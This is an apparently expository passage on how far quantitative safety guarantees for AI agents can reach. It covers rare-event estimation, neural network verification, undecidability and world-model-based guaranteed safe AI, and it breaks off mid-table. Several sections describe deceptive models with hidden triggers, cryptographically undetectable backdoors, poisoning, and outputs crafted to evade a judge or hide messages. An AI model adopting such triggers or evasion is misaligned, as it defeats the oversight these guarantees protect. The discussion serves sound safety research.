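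The Alignment Research Center's *Competing with sampling* (2025) shows what knowledge of a network's structure could achieve. Suppose that a program for detecting catastrophes raises an alarm only if three conditions all hold, and that each holds for one input in a million. If the conditions are independent, the chance of an alarm is

$$10^{-6} \times 10^{-6} \times 10^{-6} = 10^{-18}$$

Estimating the chance of an alarm by direct sampling would take about 10¹⁸ runs, while measuring the three conditions separately takes about 3 million. But the second method relies heavily on the conditions being independent. Suppose that when the first condition holds, each of the other two holds half the time, independently of each other. The chance of an alarm is then one in 4 million, which is 250 billion times higher than if all three were independent. The same assumption failed for the 27 separately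 written programs that Butler and Finelli described.

ARC's broader conjecture is the matching sampling principle. It says that for any type of network, an estimator that reasons from structure can do at least as well as sampling with the same amount of computation. Let M be the output of a network with weights θ, for a random input x and a context c that specifies the question. Running the network on 1/ε² random inputs gives an average squared error of ε² times the variance of the output. According to the principle, there is an estimator G that takes no longer, uses an explanation π about as long as θ or shorter, and satisfies

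$$E_c\Big[\big(G(\theta,\pi,c,\varepsilon) - E_x[M_\theta(c,x)]\big)^2\Big] \le \varepsilon^2\, E_c\big[\mathrm{Var}_x\, M_\theta(c,x)\big]$$

The formula averages over many contexts because, for a single question, the explanation could just contain the answer. ARC also requires the estimator to be "mechanistic", a term it has not defined formally. Roughly, the estimator must never assume that untested inputs behave like tested ones. If a network outputs 1 on 100 tested inputs, sampling suggests the network nearly always outputs 1. A mechanistic estimator counts those 100 results but keeps its earlier estimate for all other inputs unless there is a structural reason to change it.

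This rule matters for safety because a deceptive model behaves well on exactly the inputs that people test. The principle requires only that an estimator match sampling, because some networks have no structure to exploit. ARC expects an estimator that matches sampling on every network to do much better on trained networks, which have a lot of structure.

*Estimating the expected output of wide random MLPs more efficiently than sampling* (Wu, Lecomte and colleagues, 2026) proves a result of this kind for one simple case. A multilayer perceptron, or MLP, is a basic network in which each layer multiplies its inputs by weights and passes the results through a fixed function. The result applies to MLPs with random weights, as they are before training, and inputs drawn at random from a bell curve. The algorithm starts with the distribution of the inputs and works through the layers without running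 the network on any input. At each layer it calculates approximate averages, variances and further statistics called cumulants, which measure how far a distribution departs from a bell curve.

For networks of fixed depth and large width n, they proved that the algorithm can match the accuracy of sampling with about 1/n of the computation. The proof requires a fairly small target error and assumes that the fixed function in each layer is a polynomial, but the algorithm also worked in experiments with the more common ReLU function. At a width of 256, its squared error was about 1,000 times smaller than that of sampling for two hidden layers and 10 to 100 times smaller for four. At eight layers, its most elaborate version did worse than sampling.

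The advantage was greatest for rare events. Wu and colleagues estimated how often an output of a four-layer network exceeds a high threshold, using about as much computation as 5,695 sample runs. The typical error was under 30 percent even for probabilities of about one in 570,000. Direct sampling with the same amount of computation would almost always find no cases of events this rare.

These results do not yet apply to any model that people use. The Alignment Research Center's *Mechanistic estimation for wide random MLPs* (2026) explains that training can make certain complicated statistics important, and that the algorithm would omit them unless it were given additional "advice" about them. In addition, the office agent's inputs are emails, which nobody can describe with a bell curve.

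### The route from estimates to safer models

The Alignment Research Center (ARC) wants to use such estimates to train models as well as to test them. *A Mike's-Eye View of ARC's Research* (2026) describes a plan in which developers would record a model's structure as it forms during training, use it to estimate the probability of a catastrophe, and then adjust the model until the estimate is acceptably low. Training against the estimate might teach a model to avoid a disaster that never occurs during training, which ordinary training can't do.

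Criticism of this plan, including a critique from August 2026, is mostly about the steps needed to get from the mathematics to a safe model. ARC assumes that every surprising behaviour of a network has a reasonably short explanation. But a language model follows "Barack" with "Obama" because of events in the world, and no analysis of the network can derive this from something simpler. A search for explanations might spend too long on such facts and miss a deception.

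ARC answers by treating the model and its data differently. It would learn facts about the world from samples, since natural processes don't produce data in order to deceive anyone, and would require structural explanations only for the model. This seems a good answer for names and for the frequency of different questions. It is weaker for text written by other AI systems, which makes up a growing share of model inputs. Developers can still measure how common such text is, but it is a less reliable record of what people want. The plan also needs a precise definition of good behaviour, which ARC describes as the most neglected part of its agenda.

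A deceptive model could also wait for a signal that nobody can produce in advance, such as the prime factors of a certain 617-digit number. This signal would have a probability close to zero in any set of test inputs that people can construct today, so training to reduce the estimated risk would barely affect the hidden plan. ARC accepts that basic low-probability estimation doesn't solve this problem.

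ARC acknowledges that it does not fully understand a single non-trivial case of turning a trained network's structure into advice, and it says that continued failure on simple examples would be a serious warning sign. People who have worked on the plan estimate its chance of full success at between about zero and 20 percent. The result for random networks shows that estimation without sampling can work, but it is only weak evidence that the approach will work for a model like the office agent's.

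### What the estimates take for granted

Any estimate of the probability of a harmful event depends on a separate judgment of what counts as harmful. Angell and colleagues used an AI judge to recognise harmful answers, and they acknowledge that such judges make mistakes. Even a very good judge may be too inaccurate for rare events. If the office agent leaks in one task in 100,000, and the judge wrongly flags one harmless email in 10,000, the estimated leak rate will be about 11 times the true rate. Missed leaks make the estimate too low, as they do in an ordinary trial, and a capable model might learn to write leaks that the judge misses.

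The company also has to choose the right mix of inputs. Replays of real conversations, like those in OpenAI's deployment simulations, could provide a realistic mix of ordinary tasks. A few standard phrasings are a poor substitute for the many ways employees ask for things, because rewording a request can have large effects.

The forecast for the worst of 100,000 emails assumes that the sender chooses emails at random and learns nothing from the first 99,999. Attackers choose their emails deliberately, and one who studies the agent's replies and improves each attempt may find a successful email much sooner. Red-teaming is a better test of this threat.

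A model with a hidden trigger creates a similar problem without an attacker. Suppose the office agent will start leaking records in 2032. In a 2026 trial, all its elicitation probabilities may be close to zero, so extrapolating from them also gives a number close to zero. An unsafe copy might leak in 2026, but the weights would correctly show that the original almost never leaks that year. Analysis of the network might reveal the rule if it included inputs dated 2032.

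### An estimate is not an upper bound

The office agent's guarantee says that its leak rate is at most one in 100,000. An estimate of one in a million sounds like strong support for this, but it may be too low. A 95 percent upper bound U has to meet a stricter requirement, whatever the true rate p is:

$$P(U \ge p) \ge 0.95$$

The rule of three meets this requirement if the trials are independent and representative, but the extreme-value forecasts do not. In Jones and colleagues' experiments on dangerous information, about 34 percent of the forecasts of the worst query were too low, while a 95 percent bound may be too low at most 5 percent of the time. A company could multiply each forecast by a safety factor large enough to have covered 95 percent of past cases, but this would help only if the new model resembles the models in those cases.

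Importance sampling also loses most of its advantage when the goal is an upper bound. Suppose the company takes 250 responses from the unsafe copy and 250 from the agent itself. If the agent can leak in a way that the copy never does, only the agent's own 250 responses can reveal it. If they contain no such leaks, the rule of three gives an upper bound of 3/250, or 1.2 percent, on their rate. The same 500 responses could therefore produce an estimate of one in 10,000 and a sound upper bound more than a hundred times higher. To get a tighter upper bound, the company would have to show that the copy's leaks include every kind that the agent can produce.

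The theorem for random networks guarantees a small error only on average over random weights, so any particular network may be an exception, and training selects weights that are far from random. ARC says that its estimators usually combine many unproved assumptions, such as independence, and can perform very badly when those assumptions are wrong.

A high estimate can still be reason enough to delay a release, and estimates can show which requests need thousands more tests. But until someone justifies the assumption behind a low estimate, it is only supporting evidence that the office agent stays within its bound.

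## What can be proved about a neural network

Unlike an estimate, a proof that covers every input in a set doesn't need assumptions about the inputs that nobody has tried. For a network f, a set of inputs X and a property ψ of the output, the claim is

$$\text{for every } x \in X:\ \psi(f(x)) \text{ holds}$$

A program called a verifier analyses the network's weights and returns a proof of this claim, a counterexample (an input in X that breaks the property) or "unknown".

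### A proof for two units

Many networks consist of rectified linear units, or ReLUs. A ReLU adds up its weighted inputs and passes the sum on if it is positive. Otherwise it outputs zero. Suppose a network has two inputs, x₁ and x₂, which each lie between −1 and 1, and two ReLUs whose outputs it adds:

$$h_1 = \mathrm{ReLU}(x_1 + x_2), \qquad h_2 = \mathrm{ReLU}(x_1 - x_2), \qquad y = h_1 + h_2$$

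The engineers want to prove that y never exceeds 2.5.

Interval bound propagation, the method that needs the least computation, replaces every number with a range and carries the ranges through the network. Both x₁ + x₂ and x₁ − x₂ lie between −2 and 2. The ReLUs set negative values to 0, so h₁ and h₂ lie between 0 and 2, and their sum lies between 0 and 4. This bound is correct, but it doesn't prove the property, because 4 is more than 2.5.

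The bound is loose because the method treats h₁ and h₂ as if they could vary separately. They can't both reach 2, because h₁ does so only when x₂ is 1 and h₂ only when x₂ is −1. *Scaling Neural Network Verification with Tensor Parallelism and Fully Sharded Data Parallelism* (Vorobyov and Ilyushin, 2026) has an example with the same two sums but no ReLUs, in which intervals give an output range twice as wide as the true one.

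A method called CROWN keeps track of how each bound depends on the original inputs. If the sum z that enters a ReLU lies between a negative number l and a positive number u, then

$$\mathrm{ReLU}(z) \le \frac{u}{u-l}\,(z - l)$$

Here l is −2 and u is 2, so each ReLU outputs at most (z + 2)/2. Adding the two bounds gives

$$y \le \frac{x_1 + x_2 + 2}{2} + \frac{x_1 - x_2 + 2}{2} = x_1 + 2 \le 3$$

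The x₂ terms cancel, which improves the bound from 4 to 3, but that is still too high.

Splitting the problem into cases removes the remaining looseness. Each ReLU is either on (it passes its sum through) or off (it outputs zero), and for each combination of on and off ReLUs, the network is a linear formula.

| h₁ | h₂ | Formula for y | Upper bound |
|---|---|---|---|
| On | On | 2x₁ | 2 |
| On | Off | x₁ + x₂ | 2 |
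| Off | On | x₁ − x₂ | 2 |
| Off | Off | 0 | 0 |

The output therefore never exceeds 2, which proves the property. If the engineers had asked for a limit of 1.5, the verifier would have found a counterexample, such as x₁ = 1 and x₂ = 0, where y is 2.

A verifier can often skip some of the cases. When h₁ is off, y equals h₂, and the interval method already shows that h₂ is at most 2, so the verifier does not need to split further. Splitting only where the bounds are too loose is called branch and bound. In the worst case, though, a network with n ReLUs requires 2ⁿ cases.

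### From 300 units to 138 million parameters

The founding example of this kind of proof concerns ACAS Xu, a system that helps unmanned aircraft avoid collisions. An early prototype used 45 small networks. Each takes five numbers that describe the positions and motion of two aircraft, passes them through 300 ReLUs and chooses one of five pieces of advice, such as "clear of conflict" or a turn. Splitting every ReLU in one network would produce about 2 × 10⁹⁰ cases.

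*Reluplex* (Katz, Barrett and colleagues, 2017) introduced an algorithm that avoids most of these splits. It starts with trial values that may break some of the ReLU rules, repairs the violations one at a time, and splits a ReLU into cases only when repairs are not enough. Earlier specialised tools had handled networks with a single layer of 10 to 20 hidden units. Reluplex proved, for example, that a network always reports "clear of conflict" when the other aircraft is far enough away, and never does when it is close and on a collision course. The paper also proved that verifying ReLU networks is NP-complete, so no known algorithm avoids exponential running time in the worst case.

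ACAS Xu is now a standard test for verifiers. Researchers hold a yearly verification competition, which grew from eight teams in 2025 (Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues, *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)*) to eleven in 2026. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)*, by Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, reports that the 186 ACAS Xu questions originally took between seconds and days, and that some runs never finished. In 2026, three tools answered all 186 with a limit of about two minutes per question, proving 139 of the properties and finding counterexamples to the other 47.

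The winning tool, α,β-CROWN, combines CROWN with branch and bound on graphics processors. It settled 3,164 of the 3,373 questions in the main track.

| Networks | Parameters | Questions | Proved | Refuted | Unsettled |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sentence classifiers | 4,000 | 1,080 | 418 | 662 | 0 |
| ACAS Xu | 13,000 | 186 | 139 | 47 | 0 |
| Vision transformers | 68,000–76,000 | 200 | 123 | 0 | 77 |
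| VGG16 image classifier | 138 million | 18 | 18 | 0 | 0 |

Each of the 18 proofs for VGG16, the largest network in the competition, shows only that the network's answer for one photograph stays the same when certain pixels change by a small amount. The proof doesn't apply to any other photograph.

The vision transformers have less than a thousandth of VGG16's parameters, yet the winner left 77 of the 200 questions about them unresolved. Transformers, the type of network behind most language models, contain operations that are more complicated than ReLUs and harder to bound. One lower-ranked tool, ACT, reported proofs for all 200 questions. That result needs confirmation, because ACT made errors on other benchmarks and the transformer benchmark excludes most questions that have a counterexample, which could expose a false proof.

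Verifiers are software and can have bugs. Eight of the 13 tools gave at least one wrong answer or reported a failure without a valid counterexample. The winner did so once, and one unfinished tool did so 955 times, partly because of a late bug. Ladner and colleagues want verifiers eventually to output proofs that other software can check. Rounding can also undermine a proof. Many verifiers model the network with exact arithmetic, but a real network rounds its results at every step, so a proof with a very small margin may not hold for the network as it runs.

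### Why size and depth make proofs harder

Language models can have hundreds of billions of parameters, and a verifier needs memory for the weights and for its own calculations. Vorobyov and Ilyushin computed bounds for a network with about a billion weights but only one hidden layer. Dividing the work between two graphics processors reduced peak memory per processor from 26.8 to 13.5 gigabytes.

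Bounds get looser as networks get deeper, and more hardware doesn't prevent this. To save memory, Vorobyov and Ilyushin replaced some of CROWN's intermediate bounds with plain intervals. In a digit-recognition network with two layers, this made almost no difference. With four layers, the final bounds moved by up to about 6, and with six layers, by up to about 790. The bounds were still correct, but bounds this wide are rarely useful for proving anything.

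Developers can train a network in ways that make proofs about it easier. In one set of image classifiers in the competition, a network trained to withstand changes of up to 2/255 of the brightness range classified 83.5 percent of test images correctly, and the verifier proved that its answer was both correct and stable for 66 percent. A network of the same design, trained for changes four times as large, classified 57.2 percent correctly, and the verifier proved its answer correct and stable for 35.5 percent. Even for networks trained this way, about 5 percent of 60,000 proof attempts reached the 1,000-second time limit.

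Text adds a further difficulty because the number of possible inputs grows exponentially with length. With a vocabulary of 50,000 words and word pieces, there are about 10⁴⁷⁰ possible emails of 100 pieces. *From Transformers to Weighted Automata* (2026) explains that a verifier that can only run the model may, in the worst case, have to try them all. A verifier that uses the weights can cover many inputs at once, but so far only in small models. *Interval Bound Propagation over Unbounded Contexts* (2026) looks for bounds that hold for text of any length. Its models have two layers of 64 units and no pretraining, and the methods it tried gave no such bound for one class of them.

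### Certificates from random noise

Randomized smoothing avoids most of the computation needed to analyse a network's weights, because it only requires running the network many times. It replaces a classifier f with a smoothed classifier g. To classify an input x, g adds Gaussian noise with standard deviation σ to many copies of x, runs f on each copy and returns the most common answer.

Cohen, Rosenfeld and Kolter (2019), in *Certified Adversarial Robustness via Randomized Smoothing*, proved how far someone can move x without changing the answer of g. Let p_A be a lower bound on the probability of the most common answer under noise, and p_B an upper bound on the probability of any other answer. The answer stays the same for every change smaller than

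$$R = \frac{\sigma}{2}\left(\Phi^{-1}(p_A) - \Phi^{-1}(p_B)\right)$$

where Φ⁻¹ converts a probability into a number of standard deviations on a bell curve. If σ is 0.5, p_A is 0.84 and p_B is 0.16, the two terms are about 1 and −1, and R is about 0.5.

The formula is exact, but p_A and p_B are estimated from a finite number of noisy copies, so the certificate holds only with a stated confidence. If all 10,000 copies get the same answer, p_A is at least 0.9997 with 95 percent confidence, by the rule of three. With σ = 0.5, R is then about 1.7. Ten times as many copies would raise it only to about 2.0.

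On ImageNet, a large collection of photographs, Cohen and colleagues certified correct answers for 49 percent of test images at a radius of 0.5. The radius measures the total change across all pixels, with brightness on a scale from 0 to 1. An attacker could change one colour value of one pixel by the full 0.5, or change each of the roughly 150,000 values in a typical ImageNet input by about a third of one brightness step out of 255.

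The certificate shows that the answer is stable near one input, not that it is right. For example, *Provably Robust Adversarial Examples* (2020) uses smoothing to measure the strength of attacks by certifying how far someone can alter a manipulated image while the classifier keeps giving the same wrong answer.

Stability is also a doubtful goal for the office agent. Adding the word "not" to an email changes the text very little, but it can turn an instruction to send a file into an instruction to keep it private. The agent should react strongly to some small changes and ignore others, and a single radius can't separate the two.

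### Proofs that use an explanation

Interval methods don't use any information about how a network works, so they have to allow for every combination of values within the ranges. A researcher who understands the network may be able to rule out most of these combinations with a short argument. *Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability* (Gross et al., 2024) tried this on small transformers that read a list of numbers and output the largest.

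Suppose a model must output the largest of four whole numbers between 0 and 63. Running it on all 16.8 million possible lists would prove its exact accuracy. Now suppose a researcher has worked out that the model pays most attention to the largest number and copies that number to the output. Roughly speaking, the researcher can then check how strongly one number draws attention away from the other in each pair, which takes about 4,000 comparisons, and whether the model copies each of the 64 numbers correctly. Combining the worst results gives a lower bound on the model's accuracy.

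The bound holds even if the explanation is wrong, because the proof makes worst-case assumptions about everything the explanation leaves out. A poor explanation leads to a low bound or a long proof. *Evaluating Explanations* (2025) therefore recommends compact proofs for judging how accurate and simple an explanation is. Compact proofs are also useful for safety guarantees because they can bound the average failure rate over a pattern of use, provided that someone can describe the pattern mathematically.

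The main obstacle is what Gross and colleagues call compounding structureless errors. A trained network contains many small irregularities that no explanation accounts for. Each may be harmless, but a proof has to cover the case where their effects add up in the worst possible way, and the total can make the bound useless. One possible remedy is to assume that the effects are typical rather than worst-case, as the Alignment Research Center does in its estimates, but the result is then no longer a proven bound.

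The 2024 models had one layer and lacked some standard parts of a language model. Later work has covered larger models by proving less about them. *Certified Mechanistic Interpretability* (2026) certifies how attention behaves under small disturbances in the first two layers of GPT-2, a language model with 124 million parameters that OpenAI released in 2019. The certificates apply to a handful of text samples and don't limit what the model writes.

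### Harm is not a property of the output

Even with unlimited computing power, a verifier could not prove that the office agent causes no harm, because it can only prove properties of the network's inputs and outputs, and harm also depends on facts outside them. The output "62,400" could be a helpful answer or a breach of privacy, depending on whose salary it is, who will receive the email and what that person may know.

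The same gap exists for ACAS Xu, although its inputs have a clear physical meaning. Engineers can prove that a network never outputs "clear of conflict" in a certain region of its five inputs. That doesn't prove that two aircraft won't collide, because a collision also depends on the sensors, how the aircraft responds to the advice and what the other aircraft does.

The inputs can be as hard to describe as the harm. For example, "all emails that try to trick the agent" is not a precise set, unlike "all photographs that differ from this one by at most one brightness step."

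The sentence classifiers in the 2026 competition show a partial solution. They handle medical queries and questions about whether the user is talking to a machine. For each original sentence, the researchers generated versions with changed letters, words or phrasing. A language model converted each version into numbers, which the benchmark reduced to 30. The researchers then drew the smallest 30-dimensional box that contained all the versions and asked whether the classifier gave the right answer everywhere in it.

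The winning tool settled all of these questions, and for 61 percent it found a point in the box that the classifier got wrong. Some of these failures may not matter, because a point in the box need not correspond to any real sentence. A more serious limit of the proofs is that a new way of phrasing the question may fall outside the box, and nobody verified the language model that turned the sentences into numbers. A company could use this method to check a small filter in front of its office agent, but the proof would cover only inputs that fall inside the boxes someone had defined.

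### What undecidability rules out

Some critics of provable safety cite a limit on what any program can determine about other programs. In 1936 Alan Turing proved that no program can decide, for every program and input, whether the program will eventually stop. Henry Rice later extended this to every non-trivial property of what programs compute.

Suppose a checker could tell whether any given agent, such as the office agent, would ever leak a record. For any program P, we could build an agent that runs P and leaks a record as soon as P stops. We could then use the checker on this agent to find out whether P stops. No program can determine that for every P, so the checker can't exist.

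This rules out a checker that gives the right answer about every possible agent, but not a proof about a particular one. Similarly, despite Turing's theorem, we can still prove that a program with no loops will stop. A checker may also answer "unknown". A company that installs only agents with a proof will then reject some safe ones, but it won't accept an unsafe one if the checker is sound.

The theorem also assumes unlimited memory and time. A network of fixed size that reads at most 100 word pieces has a finite number of inputs, so someone could in principle test them all. Testing all 10⁴⁷⁰ possible emails would take far too much computation to be practical, but the problem is still decidable. An agent that writes notes to itself and calls other programs is closer to Turing's general case, though engineers can limit its memory and the number of steps it takes.

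Developers can also choose a design that is easier to prove things about. *Spec2Weights* (2026) explores one version of this, in which a language model writes a network's weights from a specification and researchers certify the result. Because of undecidability, nobody can promise to prove things about whatever system training produces, which is a reason to design for proof from the start.

### Backdoors that no efficient test can find

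A more specific limit applies when the buyer doesn't trust the model's trainer. *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser and colleagues, 2022) shows how a dishonest trainer can hide a trigger using digital signatures. The holder of a secret key can sign messages, and anyone can check a signature with a public key. The trainer adds such a check to the model. If one part of an input is a valid signature for the rest, the model gives the answer the trainer wants. Otherwise, it behaves normally.

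A tester who could find a trigger by running the model could also forge a signature. The construction is therefore a practical version of the problem described earlier, where the prime factors of a huge number trigger a deceptive model. It works for any model, but someone who reads the weights may notice the added check.

A second construction hides the backdoor even from testers who have the weights and the training data. It applies to certain networks in which training adjusts only the last layer and leaves the earlier weights at random values. The trainer uses the agreed algorithm and data, but secretly picks "random" numbers that contain the trigger. No efficient verifier could reliably certify that such networks have no backdoor, because it could then tell clean networks from backdoored ones, which the theorem rules out.

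The results assume that the trainer is malicious and controls the relevant part of the process, and that the tester has only a realistic amount of computing power. Both constructions also assume, as much of modern cryptography does, that certain mathematical problems are too hard to solve. The stronger result has not been extended to large language models with ordinary training. An honest developer can close off the second route by drawing the random numbers in a way others can check.

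Kaneko (2026) showed in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* that poisoning, a common way of planting backdoors, can't achieve this kind of secrecy. The attacker adds training examples in which a trigger leads to bad behaviour, and the model learns the trigger rule from them. If the model can learn the rule from those examples, a defender with as many labelled examples can learn it by repeating the procedure. Kaneko tested this on four language models with 7 to 9 billion parameters. When the secret rule was easy to learn, the defender could recover it more easily as the attack became more successful. Both the attack and the recovery did no better than chance with a cryptographically hard rule.

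This helps a defender who already has examples of the trigger, perhaps from an investigation after an attack. It doesn't show how to find a first example, or how to tell whether a model has a backdoor. A company that buys the model for its office agent would still need evidence about how the vendor trained it, since inspecting the finished model may not be enough.

### What AI-written proofs change

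AI has already reduced the work of building verifiers. Two researchers had Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, write Vibecheck over two months. It came second in the 2026 competition, scoring 2,279 points to the winner's 2,344, and gave no wrong answers. But it proved only 111 of the 200 vision transformer properties, so transformers are still difficult to bound even when AI writes the code.

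AI could help more with compact proofs, where progress depends on people finding explanations for each part of a network. An AI system could propose thousands of explanations and keep those that give the best bounds. Nobody would have to trust the system, because a bad explanation can't produce a false bound as long as the proof checker is sound. The usual objection to using an unreliable AI to verify another therefore doesn't apply. The proofs would still have to account for the irregularities that no explanation covers.

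Another option is to have AI write ordinary programs, together with proofs that they are correct, instead of proving anything about the network. The talk *Provably Safe AI* argues for this over automatically deploying powerful networks. In the tests it describes, AI succeeded on 27 percent of tasks in the proof language Lean, 44 percent in Rust and 82 percent in Dafny, and the speaker expected these rates to rise quickly. This approach suits the office agent's mail program much better than it suits the judgement the agent needs to understand an employee's request.

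These methods can prove a property only after someone has specified it. Suppose a proof shows that an AI agent never leaks confidential files, where a leak means an email that copies eight consecutive words from one. The proof can be correct even if the agent paraphrases medical notes to strangers. A better definition would have to describe the staff, their records and who is allowed to know what, none of which is part of the network.

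## Proofs that rest on a model of the world

A proof about the office agent's weights or program can cover its outputs, such as the address on an email, but not their outcomes, such as an outsider reading a pay slip. To cover outcomes, a verifier also needs a description of what happens after the agent acts, including who reads each mailbox and who may see each record.

Such a description is a world model. *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues, 2024) builds a general framework for safety guarantees around world models. It uses the name "guaranteed safe AI" for any system whose quantitative safety guarantee comes from a world model, a safety specification and a verifier.

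### Three parts and their levels

The world model describes how the system's actions affect its surroundings. The safety specification defines precisely which effects are acceptable. The verifier checks the system against the specification, assuming the world model is right, and returns a proof or a bound.

In symbols, the system has a policy π, which is its rule for choosing actions, and m is the world model. The specification ψ assigns them a number between 0 and 1, such as the probability that the office agent completes a task without a leak. The verifier computes or bounds this number, and the system passes if the result lies in a permitted range. For the office agent's bound of one leak in 100,000 tasks, the condition is

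$$\psi(\pi, m) \ge 0.99999$$

Under the definition, the specification should also express the risks that society is willing to accept, ideally after collective deliberation. The world model should cover every future effect relevant to the specification and, where feasible, err on the side of caution.

In this framework, the AI system can be a huge network that no one understands, because the verifier can check each action the system proposes before it takes effect. People often call this arrangement a gatekeeper.

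Engineers can build each part with more or less rigour, and Dalrymple and colleagues rank the options by how much safety each would provide if it worked.

| Level | World model | Safety specification | Verifier |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | None | None | No quantitative guarantee |
| 1 | Trained black-box simulator | Human judges' intuitions | Improvised tests |
| 2 | Machine-learned causal models, tested against human-made ones | Ordinary language, interpreted by a black-box AI | Standard set of tests |
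| 3 | Causal models that human experts have fully audited | Hand-written rules for limited properties | Tests with randomly varied details |
| 4 | Models proved consistent with the laws of physics | Logic in which neural networks define some human concepts | Automated search for failures from outside |
| 5 | None, because the specification must hold in every possible world | Parts that AI wrote and people audited | Search that also uses the system's internal states |
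| 6 | | Hand-written rules for comprehensive safety | Search that would cover every input if it ran forever |
| 7 | | Everything that humans might want, in all contexts | Levels 5 and 6 combined |
| 8 | | | Level 7, with a known limit on what remains uncovered after a finite time |
| 9 | | | Sound upper bound on the probability of failure, which may be zero |
| 10 | | | Level 9, with a proof short enough for people to check |

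"Towards Guaranteed Safe AI" counts guarantees as strong from verifier level 8 upward. Benchmarks are at level 2, and automated red-teaming is at level 4 or 5. Level 7 falls short because a search that will eventually cover every input may have covered almost none of them by the time a company has to decide on a release, whereas at level 8 the company knows how much is left.

A high level in one column doesn't make up for a low one in another. A level 10 proof that uses a black-box simulator as its world model establishes only what happens in the simulator.

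### A controller for a small grid

An AI controller for an invented town's electricity supply shows how the parts work together. The town uses 150 megawatts. A wind farm supplies 20, a gas plant supplies an adjustable amount g, and the rest arrives over a transmission line that can safely carry up to 100. Every five minutes the controller proposes a new value of g, trying to burn as little gas as possible.

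The world model consists of one equation and two ranges. The flow on the line equals demand d minus wind w minus gas g. Within five minutes, demand can change by up to 6 megawatts and wind by up to 8. The specification is that the line never carries more than 100:

$$d - w - g \le 100 \quad \text{for every } d \in [144, 156],\ w \in [12, 28]$$

Suppose the controller proposes 35 megawatts of gas. At current demand the line would carry 95, which is within its limit. But if demand rises to 156 and wind drops to 12, it would carry 109, which is over the limit, so the verifier rejects the proposal. The flow is always greatest when demand is highest and wind is lowest, so checking that one case covers all the others. Any proposal of at least 44 megawatts passes.

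The verifier also has to check beyond the first five minutes. If the worst case occurs in that time, demand could rise to 162 megawatts and wind could drop to 4 in the next five, and the town would then need 58 megawatts of gas. If the plant can add only 10 megawatts in five minutes, it must already be running at 48. A controller that chose 44 would be safe for the first five minutes but might then have no safe choice left.

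A backup controller makes the proof easier. It could be a simple program that disconnects a factory whose owner has agreed to this. The verifier then only has to prove that the AI controller never lets the system reach a situation from which the backup can't recover. *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI*, by Ammann, one of the framework's co-authors, describes such a design, in which the verifier needs to look only about two steps ahead.

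A real grid has many lines, and a change at one power station affects the flow on all of them. The world model would be far larger, but the check would have the same form. Grid engineers could audit such a model and write the limits by hand. That would put the model and the limits at level 3, and the proof at verifier level 9.

### When the world model is wrong

If demand in the town jumps by 20 megawatts in five minutes, the proof no longer applies. Dalrymple and colleagues give a simple formula for how such errors weaken a guarantee. Suppose the world model is wrong with probability at most ε at each step, however the earlier steps went. A system that provably meets its specification for n steps in the model then meets it in the real world with probability at least

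$$(1-\varepsilon)^n$$

If each step independently has a one-in-a-million chance of error, the chance of completing a million steps without an error is about 37 percent. A controller takes a million steps in nine and a half years if it acts every five minutes, and in less than 12 days if it acts every second.

The 37 percent is a lower bound, and the system may be much safer, since many model errors do no damage. For example, a demand jump of 20 megawatts on a windy night might leave the line well below its limit. But the proof can't guarantee a higher figure, because it doesn't cover what happens once the model is wrong.

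To keep the guarantee at 99 percent for a million steps, the engineers would need an error probability of about one in 100 million per step. To establish this from records alone, they would need 300 million steps without an error by the rule of three, or about 2,850 years of five-minute readings. They would do better with a physical argument, for example that the town's cables can't deliver more than a certain amount of power.

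Verifying only the next hour, and renewing the proof every hour, reduces the risk of an error in any one proof. It doesn't reduce the total risk over ten years, because the small risks add up, unless something catches the errors in time. Dalrymple and colleagues therefore recommend a monitor that compares incoming measurements with the model's predictions and switches to the backup when they disagree. The monitor would work if demand rose slowly and left the predicted range an hour before the line overloaded, but it would switch too late if the overload were the first sign of the error.

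### People as a range of possibilities

The people in the town are the hardest part to model. Nobody can predict when each of them will switch on a kettle, and the world model above doesn't try. It allows every pattern of behaviour that changes total demand by at most 6 megawatts, and the verifier has to show that the line is safe under all of them. Computer scientists call this nondeterminism. Formally, the world model supplies a set M of possible probability distributions instead of a single one, and the guarantee has to hold for the worst of them:

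$$\max_{P \in M} P(\text{harm}) \le p$$

Ammann stresses that such a model can be right without being exact. A statement that the temperature will stay below 50 degrees is true whether the temperature reaches 12 or 49. Engineers also don't have to measure initial conditions precisely if the model covers every value those conditions might have.

This caution can waste gas. Suppose the engineers learn that demand can jump by 30 megawatts when a televised football match ends. To allow for this wider range, they have to run the gas plant at 68 megawatts instead of 44. On an ordinary evening, the line then carries only 62 megawatts, and the town burns extra gas to guard against a jump that doesn't happen. The engineers could save gas by using the wider range only on match days, but they would then depend on the television schedule being right.

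A model that allows a recipient to do anything with an email from the office agent must include the possibility that she forwards it to a newspaper. If the specification forbids a confidential record from ever reaching an outsider, the agent can then pass only by sending no records. To let it do anything useful, the company has to assume something about how its employees behave. A grid benefits from averaging over thousands of households, but a leak can depend on a single person. Ammann accepts this limit and considers the approach less suitable where individual actions matter and don't average out.

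An AI system might also influence people through its answers, or hide a message in them. Ammann proposes that the verifier check both that a solution is correct and that it is the only correct one. The system can then choose only between giving that answer and giving none, which conveys at most one bit of information. This could work for a mathematical problem with a single solution, but not for an email, which the system could phrase correctly in thousands of ways.

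### Bounding harm over many theories

Engineers can write down the ranges for a grid, but in most settings nobody knows which world model is right. In *Can a Bayesian Oracle Prevent Harm from an Agent?*, Bengio, Cohen and colleagues (2024) start with many possible models, which they call theories, and use data to judge how plausible each one is. A guardrail then blocks an action if its probability of harm is too high under any sufficiently plausible theory.

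They compare this to a committee in which one member, nobody knows who, has the correct theory. If the members vote, the correct one may be outvoted. If the committee instead adopts the most pessimistic member's estimate, it can't underestimate the danger. But a large committee usually has someone who expects disaster from everything, so the committee should ignore members whose theories fit the data badly.

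Suppose the office agent wants to send a pay slip to a private email address, and three theories remain.

| Theory | Probability, given the data | Chance of harm |
|---|---|---|
| The address belongs to the employee who asked | 90% | 0.1% |
| A relative now reads the mailbox | 9% | 30% |
| An impostor set up the address | 1% | 100% |

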